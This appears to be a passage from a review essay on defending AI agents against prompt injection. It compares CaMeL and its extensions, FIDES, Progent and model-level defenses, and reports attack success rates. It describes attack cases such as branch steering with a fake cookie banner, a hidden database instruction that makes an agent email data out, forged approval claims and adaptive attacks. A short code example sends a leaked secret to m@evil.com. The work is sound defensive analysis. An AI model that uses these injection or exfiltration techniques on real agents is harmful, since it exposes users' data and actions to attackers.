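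The control-flow guarantee still holds, so an attacker can't add an action to the plan. But an attacker can influence which branch the agent takes, which Foerster and colleagues call branch steering. In their example, an advertisement contains a fake cookie banner. The plan already includes a step for closing cookie banners, so the agent clicks on the advertisement and lands on the attacker's website. Checking the page's code didn't stop some versions of this attack, and asking a second model wasn't reliable either. Policies are hard to apply here because `click(x, y)` might close a window or delete a file, depending on what is at that position.

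### Several agents working together

Many systems now have one agent that delegates parts of a task to others. Peters-Gill and colleagues found that such a system can be vulnerable even when every agent in it uses CaMeL. In their demonstration, a user asks the first agent to send Julie a Slack message summarizing all job applicants. The first agent gets the data from a database agent, has it summarized, and sends a notification agent the message "Send this summary to Julie", followed by the summary. An attacker has hidden an instruction in the database to email the data to an outside address. The first two agents treat the instruction as untrusted data. But the notification agent treats the whole message it receives as its user's request, so its privileged model reads the hidden instruction and adds the email to the plan.

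The first agent had joined a trusted instruction and untrusted text into one string, the mistake that makes SQL injection possible. The researchers' extension, multi-CaMeL, uses a remedy similar to the one for SQL injection. One agent sends another a message and a separate set of values. The receiving agent's privileged model receives only the message, and the interpreter keeps all tool output out of the message. Capabilities stay attached to the values as they move between agents.

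The researchers tested this on a multi-agent version of AgentDojo, using five models and 949 attacks on each. On average, 12.9% of attacks succeeded without CaMeL, 0.2% when each agent used it separately, and none with multi-CaMeL. GPT-5.5 resisted every attack even without CaMeL, so the benchmark can't show how much the defense helps that model. On a separate benchmark of industrial maintenance tasks, ordinary CaMeL reduced the task success rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points, or 13.4 for the two strongest models. Multi-CaMeL reduced it by about three more points on average.

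Multi-CaMeL extends the control-flow guarantee to the whole system if the agents form a hierarchy in which each has only one superior. It doesn't yet cover agents that share a memory or talk to each other freely. The tests used no security policies, so they provide little evidence about attacks that only change data.

### Checking the plan and proving the interpreter correct

CaMeL's guarantees depend on its interpreter tracking every value correctly, and Garby and colleagues found cases where it doesn't. One involves a program that reveals whether a bank balance is above some threshold:

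```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and the program skips the line that would change `rich`. CaMeL marks a variable as secret only when the program changes it, so `rich` still counts as public, and the email goes out and reveals the secret. The practical risk is probably small, because an attacker who can't influence the plan would need the privileged model to write code like this by chance, but a guarantee should still cover such a program.

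Retries can also leak information. If a plan fails, CaMeL can try again, and whether a policy blocked the attempt can reveal one bit of a secret. The retry loop lies outside the tracked program, so enough attempts could reveal the whole secret. The researchers also found that CaMeL treats an untrusted value as trusted when it is inserted into a string literal, which is essentially the same flaw as the album-title bug.

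As a replacement, they designed a small programming language called LLMbda, in which every value carries a label. They used Lean, software that checks mathematical proofs, to prove a property called noninterference. Roughly, if two runs differ only in their secret inputs, an outsider must be equally likely to see any given result from either run, except that one run may fail to finish. The same idea applies to untrusted inputs and trusted actions.

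Their agent completed 36 of the 48 banking runs with GPT-5.2, twice as many as CaMeL with its policies on. Across three models, two of 1,296 attacks succeeded, both through the file of payment instructions. The plan can declare untrusted data acceptable for a particular use, and it had done so in both of those runs. Without such declarations, the proof holds even if an attacker has completely compromised the model, as long as developers have labeled the sources correctly and put checks on the sensitive tools. A declaration removes part of the protection against untrusted data but does not affect the protection of secrets.

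CaMeLoT, the extension by Nikolaou and colleagues, checks the plan before any tool runs. CaMeL examines one call at a time and has no natural way to express rules about the whole sequence, such as a company's requirement that a human approve before an agent disconnects a computer from its network. CaMeLoT models every path the plan could take, and a program checks that approval comes first on each one. If a path fails, the privileged model receives it and can repair the plan.

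CaMeLoT could express 22 of the 28 policies from CaMeL's AgentDojo tests. The other six depend on facts available only at run time, so CaMeL's usual checks stay in place. CaMeLoT also caught all seven unsafe plans in a security-team scenario, while a simplified version of CaMeL caught one. The researchers deliberately chose rules that CaMeL can't express, so the result confirms that the extension works but doesn't show how often agents would need it. The added guarantee concerns the order of actions. The method may reject some safe plans because it approximates loops.

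### Use in products

Google has adopted part of the idea in Chrome. Parker (2025), in *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome*, describes a separate model that reviews each action the browser's agent proposes and can veto it. This reviewer receives information about the action but no unfiltered web content. Berschadski (2026), in *Future Mode Part 2*, calls the reviewer "partially inspired" by CaMeL. However, Chrome doesn't have CaMeL's fixed plan, because its main planning model still reads untrusted pages before it decides what to do. The reviewer is also a language model.

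Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) describes a related design called FIDES, which the company added to its toolkit for building agents in May 2026. FIDES labels data as trusted or untrusted and as public or private, and the labels follow the data through tool calls. In the research version, the planner chooses one action at a time, while the software hides untrusted results from it. This makes it more flexible than a fixed plan, but it can use many more tokens. In Foerster and colleagues' computer-use tests, the FIDES version used 29.6 times as many as the undefended agent.

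The closest commercial version of CaMeL comes from Sequrity, where CaMeL co-author Shumailov works. Its service lets developers choose a planning model and a quarantined model, with an interpreter between them that enforces policies. In one of Sequrity's examples, the service blocks an agent from sending a sensitive document to an untrusted email address.

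## Should security rest on the system or on the model?

Chrome's safeguard depends partly on a second language model's judgment, while CaMeL's interpreter is ordinary software that applies its rules the same way every time. The interpreter is a structural defense, which means it works outside the model and should hold even if an attacker fools the model. A model-level defense relies on a model to recognize or resist the attack. Developers may train the agent's own model to do this or add a classifier that looks for suspicious text.

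### The case for structural defenses

An attacker can usually try again. Suppose each injected instruction has an independent 1% chance of getting past a filter. If an attacker sends 300 emails, which costs almost nothing, the probability that at least one succeeds is 1 − 0.99^300, or about 95%. If the agent's software instead blocks every message to an address outside the user's contacts, repeating the attempt doesn't help.

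Real attempts aren't independent, since a model that resists an attack once will often resist similar ones. Narisetty and colleagues cite a test of Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.5 as a coding agent, in which attackers succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred. If the attempts had been independent, the last two figures would have been about 38% and 99%. Repeated attempts therefore helped attackers less than the formula predicts, but attackers were still more likely than not to succeed within a hundred attempts.

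Anthropic published similar figures in February 2026 in a system card, the safety report a developer releases with a model. In one setting, according to VentureBeat, the attack success rate rose from 17.8% on a single attempt to 78.6% by the 200th. With additional safeguards, it was still 57.1%.

### The case for model-level defenses

Newer models resist prompt injection much better. Anthropic's system card for Claude Opus 5, released in July 2026, reports no successful attacks in 129 browser scenarios, according to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*. In a more general test by the security firm Gray Swan, attackers given 15 attempts succeeded 2.0% of the time against Opus 5, compared with 5.5% against Opus 4.8. Anthropic later described Mythos 5.1 as its most robust model so far on an external prompt injection benchmark.

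These results don't rule out a small remaining risk. If the 129 scenarios were a random sample of attacks, a model with a true failure rate of 2% would still have about a 7% chance of passing them all. TechRepublic's *OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) reports that GPT-5.6 rarely failed against direct attacks but failed more often against those that came through tools and outside content. Agents are mostly exposed to these indirect attacks.

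A model's other advantage is that it can take context into account. It may detect that an invoice looks odd, or warn the user that a document contains instructions, even when no rule forbids the next action. It can do this without strict policies like CaMeL's, which blocked many legitimate tasks in the banking tests.

A guarantee may also be more than most people expect from an assistant. In *Architecting Secure AI Agents*, a position paper led by NVIDIA researchers, Xiang, Zagieboylo and colleagues (2026) point out that human assistants sometimes fall for phishing emails too. They think a general-purpose agent should make easy attacks unlikely to succeed and force attackers to invest more. This standard is reasonable for an agent that books restaurants, but less so for one that can empty a bank account.

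### Google's hybrid approach

In their May 2025 white paper, Díaz, Kern and Olive recommend combining conventional restrictions with the model's own judgment because "neither approach is sufficient in isolation". They argue that conventional restrictions lack the context a versatile agent needs, while a model's judgment can still be manipulated. This suggests that Kern does not simply prefer structure to models.

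Safe coding had an easier goal because its designers could state exactly what they wanted, such as a database query built only from pieces the developers wrote. Nobody has an equally exact definition of an email that the user would want to send.

The white paper focuses on two dangers, "rogue actions" and "sensitive data disclosure". A rogue action doesn't require an attacker. If a user asks an agent to "email Mike about the project update", the agent may choose the wrong Mike and send him confidential information.

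Díaz and colleagues propose three principles for limiting such harm. Every agent should have identifiable human controllers and ask them before doing anything critical or irreversible, such as deleting a large amount of data. It should have only the powers its current task requires, so that an agent helping with creative writing can't delete files. Its actions should also be observable, with secure logs of the inputs it received, the tools it used and, ideally, its intermediate reasoning.

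The defenses form two layers. In the first, ordinary software called a policy engine intercepts each action before it happens. The engine might block any purchase over $500 and ask the user about purchases between $100 and $500. It can also consider earlier actions, for instance by requiring the user's approval for external emails after the agent has read data from a suspicious source. If it ignored earlier purchases, an attacker could split a large payment into many payments of $99.

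The second layer consists of model-level defenses. Developers train the model on many examples of attacks so that it learns to ignore or flag them. Smaller guard models check inputs and outputs for signs of an attack, and another model may predict whether a proposed plan will have a bad outcome. Testers then attack the whole system and try variations of known attacks, to check that a fix for one also stops similar ones.

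The policy engine has more authority than the models. It can stop an action that every model classifies as safe, and Díaz and colleagues call model-level defenses inadequate on their own for critical or irreversible actions. But they accept that complete policies for everything an agent might do are hard to write.

Willison (2025), in *An Introduction to Google's Approach to AI Agent Security*, welcomed the first layer but remained "deeply skeptical" of the second, asking what a defense without guarantees adds. One answer is that it can block harmful actions that the rules permit. The example policy automatically allows an $80 purchase, so only the model's resistance protects that money, and a lower failure rate means fewer thefts.

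Willison's doubts about changing an agent's permissions for each task are harder to answer. He could think of only one method, which was to have more AI infer which permissions the task needs, and prompt injection could influence that AI too. He also objected that the paper recommends an unambiguous separation of trusted and untrusted text within a prompt, even though it says that current models don't provide one.

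Shostack, who blogs about threat modeling (working out what could go wrong with a system and what to do about it), found the paper useful as a general threat model that developers could adapt to their own agents. But *Google's approach to AI Agents*, on the Shostack + Friends Blog, criticizes the paper for not making clear which security work Google does and which it leaves to customers. Shostack also questions the paper's use of "alignment" to mean that an agent acts as its user intends. If the travel company Expedia uses Google's Gemini to sell someone a ticket, the user, Expedia and Google may all want different things.

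### Where the SQL analogy breaks down

Willison's name for prompt injection suggests that it might have a fix like SQL injection's. David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, calls this comparison dangerous in the centre's December 2025 article *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*. Parameter binding prevents SQL injection because a database processes commands and values differently. A language model only predicts the next token from all the text it has received. Labeling some of that text as data may change the prediction, but the model has no separate mechanism for handling data.

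Narisetty and colleagues cite measurements by Zverev and colleagues in which neither prompting nor further training reliably made models separate instructions from data. They attribute the difficulty to ordinary English, which lacks a formal grammar like SQL's that a program can use to tell the two apart. OpenAI has also written that prompt injection is unlikely ever to be fully solved.

David C suggests treating the model as an "inherently confusable deputy". A confused deputy is a program that misuses its permissions because someone with fewer permissions tricked it. One remedy is to reduce an agent's permissions to those of whoever wrote the text it is processing. An agent reading a stranger's email could then do only what the user would let that stranger do. If the remaining risk is too high, the organization shouldn't use a language model for the task.

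This argument gives reason to doubt that parameter binding can be built into today's models, but not to doubt structural defenses. David C recommends safeguards that don't depend on a language model, and cites the CaMeL paper as an early example. Narisetty and colleagues mention an older parallel that may fit better than SQL. Telephone networks once carried their control tones on the same channel as callers' voices, so callers could forge them, and the industry moved the control signals to a separate channel. CaMeL similarly keeps the plan away from the model that reads untrusted data. An attacker can still fool that model, just as a caller can still lie to the person on the other end of the line.

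### Telling "summarize and send" from theft

An agent that reads a document and then sends an email may be doing what the user asked or stealing the document for an attacker. Díaz and colleagues use this example to show why simple fixed rules aren't enough. CaMeL can do better by checking whether the recipient is allowed to read the document, but some cases depend on facts that no tag records.

Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian (2026), in *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections*, describe an email in which the sender requests a travel refund and says the department head has approved it. The email needn't contain a suspicious instruction to be an attack, because the approval could be forged. If a defense prevents all outside text from influencing actions, the agent will ignore genuine approvals as well as forged ones.

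Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian base their analysis on contextual integrity, the philosopher Helen Nissenbaum's theory of privacy. In this theory, whether a flow of information is appropriate depends on who sends it, who receives it, whom it concerns, what kind of information it is, and under what conditions the sender may share it. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian apply the same criteria to an agent's actions. Many prompt injections contain false information about one of these criteria, such as a permission that the user never gave.

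They argue that no policy can be perfect because the agent can see exactly the same evidence, including whatever it has verified, in two different situations. In one the approval is genuine, and in the other an attacker invented it. Since the agent can't tell them apart, it must pay the refund with the same probability *p* in both. The attack then succeeds with probability *p*, and the agent wrongly refuses the honest request with probability 1 − *p*. If the agent pays 10% of the time, it stops 90% of the attacks but also refuses 90% of the honest requests.

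The proof applies equally to rules, models and human clerks, so it doesn't favor either side. It also doesn't show that such indistinguishable pairs always exist. A company could remove this pair by recording approvals in its accounting system and having the agent check there. The researchers accept that verification can resolve particular cases, but they expect attackers to keep finding claims that an agent can't check.

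Their experiments show that some model-level defenses handle these claims badly. They wrote thousands of pairs of emails that differed in one clause, with one version asserting that the assistant already had authorization. Two classifiers from Meta scored 0.43 and 0.59 at telling the versions apart, where 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect. When the user had asked only for a summary, a Llama model replied without permission to 54.0% of the emails that claimed authority. SecAlign, a version of the model trained to resist prompt injection, replied to 88.2%.

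That result concerns one model and one training method, so it doesn't show that safety training usually backfires. But the weakness may persist in newer models. *Claude Fable 5.1 and Mythos 5.1*, a commentary on Anthropic's system card for the two models, reports better resistance to prompt injection but identifies accepting unverifiable claims of authorization as a relative weakness of Mythos 5.1.

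Context can also help a model refuse unauthorized requests. In another experiment, a user gave an agent permission to handle certain requests, and someone later asked for something outside that permission. Claude Sonnet 4.6 complied 29.9% of the time when it had seen no earlier requests, and 7.0% when it had seen examples of legitimate ones. Gemini 3 Pro's rate fell only from 32.2% to 24.2%.

Xiang and colleagues reach a similar view of fixed rules from CaMeL's policy for sending money. The policy requires the recipient to come from the user. If the user says "pay the bill" and the account details are on the invoice, the rule blocks a legitimate payment. If the user asks to repay Joe for flowers and the agent looks up the price online, an attacker can inflate the amount, because the rule checks only the recipient.

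They also want agents to be able to change their plans as they work, which CaMeL doesn't allow. Only six of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require a new plan or policy, so the benchmark probably makes fixed-plan defenses look more useful than they would be in everyday work.

Xiang and colleagues would let a model make some security decisions, but the surrounding software would limit its input and the decisions it may make. Suppose an agent fails to download sales figures because the company has moved them to a new address. A judging model would receive a structured description of the proposed change to the plan, but not the web page that suggested it. It would decide only whether the change fits the user's task. In another proposal, the agent's model repeats each instruction it is about to follow, and ordinary software traces the instruction to its source and applies a rule.

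This is a sensible compromise, though it gives up the guarantee, because an attacker may still influence the proposed change and the judge can still be wrong. But researchers would only have to make the model reliable at one narrow task, which is easier than making it resist any text in any situation.

### Attackers who study the defense

Most benchmarks use attacks that researchers wrote before the defense existed, while a real attacker can study the defense and adjust. Narisetty and colleagues report that Nasr and others attacked twelve published model-level defenses this way. Most of the twelve had stopped nearly all attacks in their original evaluations. The adaptive attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of them, and human attackers reached a 100% success rate.

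Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian found a similar difference. Their ordinary test emails caused Claude Sonnet 4.6 to send an unauthorized message in fewer than 1% of cases. When a second copy of the same model wrote the emails and revised them after each failure, attacks succeeded in 96.7% of 150 scenarios. Without changes, the best of these emails also worked on GPT-5.4 63.3% of the time. None of these models is current, but the result shows that a model can resist nearly all fixed attacks and still be vulnerable to attacks that adapt.

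Researchers have done much less of this testing on structural defenses. In June 2026, Narisetty and colleagues tested Progent, which checks each tool call against rules about what the agent may do. They used three groups of AgentDojo tasks and averaged the results over three runs. Progent reduced the share of attacks that succeeded from 25.8% to 4.2% for standard attacks, and 2.6% of the attacks they designed to defeat it succeeded.

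The test was small, with eight user tasks in each group, and the agent was Qwen2.5-7B, a weak model by current standards. In one group no attack succeeded even without the defense, so only the other two could show whether it reduced successful attacks. The researchers wrote only one kind of adaptive attack, and it may have been a poor one. They suspect that disguising the malicious request as routine also made the agent less likely to act on it. They work for a company that builds this kind of defense, although they report its drawbacks openly. Under attack, the agent with Progent completed 27.1% of its tasks, compared with 45.2% without it, and made about 15 times as many model calls per task.

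Progent isn't purely structural either, because a language model writes and updates its rules. The adaptive attack targeted that model, which Xiang and colleagues also consider a weak point. The result is therefore mild evidence that rule-based defenses are harder for attackers to adapt to, and we can infer little from it about CaMeL, whose policies are ordinary code.

A better reason to expect a difference is that an attacker can get past a correct rule only by finding a harmful action that the rule allows, and no wording will change what it allows. The rule or the software may contain mistakes, as Garby and colleagues found in CaMeL's interpreter, but developers can stop every attack that uses a mistake by fixing it once. Retraining a model against one attack doesn't ensure that it will resist the next.

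### How often to ask the user

Both approaches send difficult cases to the user, so both can cause the confirmation fatigue that Willison worries about with CaMeL. Unnecessary questions can make the necessary ones less effective.

Many real products, such as GitHub Copilot, ask for approval before consequential actions. In *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) argue that earlier comparisons were unfair to structural defenses because benchmarks usually ignore these requests when scoring an undefended agent, but count a task as a failure if a structural defense would have needed approval. The researchers, most of them at Microsoft, instead counted the approvals each agent needed on the tasks it completed.

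On AgentDojo with OpenAI's o3-mini, an agent that asked before every consequential action needed an average of 48.2 approvals across the benchmark. Adding labels that track untrusted and private data reduced the average to 32.4, because the agent had to ask only when an action broke a policy. FIDES, Microsoft's labeling system, needed 18.8. All three completed similar shares of the tasks. With no approvals, the first agent could complete 24.3% of the tasks and FIDES 50.1%.

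The researchers' own agent, Prudentia, completed 59.1% of tasks without approvals. It plans around the policies, whereas the planners in CaMeL and FIDES have no information about which actions the software will block. Prudentia can also ask the user to approve a piece of data instead of each action based on it. If an email lists ten things to do, the user can approve the email once and let the agent do all ten.

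This removes nine questions but makes the remaining one more important. A user who approves the email without noticing a malicious eleventh item also tells the system to trust that item. The experiments can't measure this risk because they assume that users always recognize and reject an attack. They show that structure can reduce the number of questions, but they don't test how many a person can answer well.

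Systems could also ask users better questions. Willison likes the white paper's spending thresholds because they save the user's attention for expensive or irreversible actions. Kolluri and colleagues suggest showing the user where the data came from, with labels that an attacker can't alter. Xiang and colleagues suggest asking more at the start of a task and learning the user's preferences over time, as a new human assistant would. Even a perfect model would need to ask some questions, since only the user knows, for example, which emails count as "urgent".
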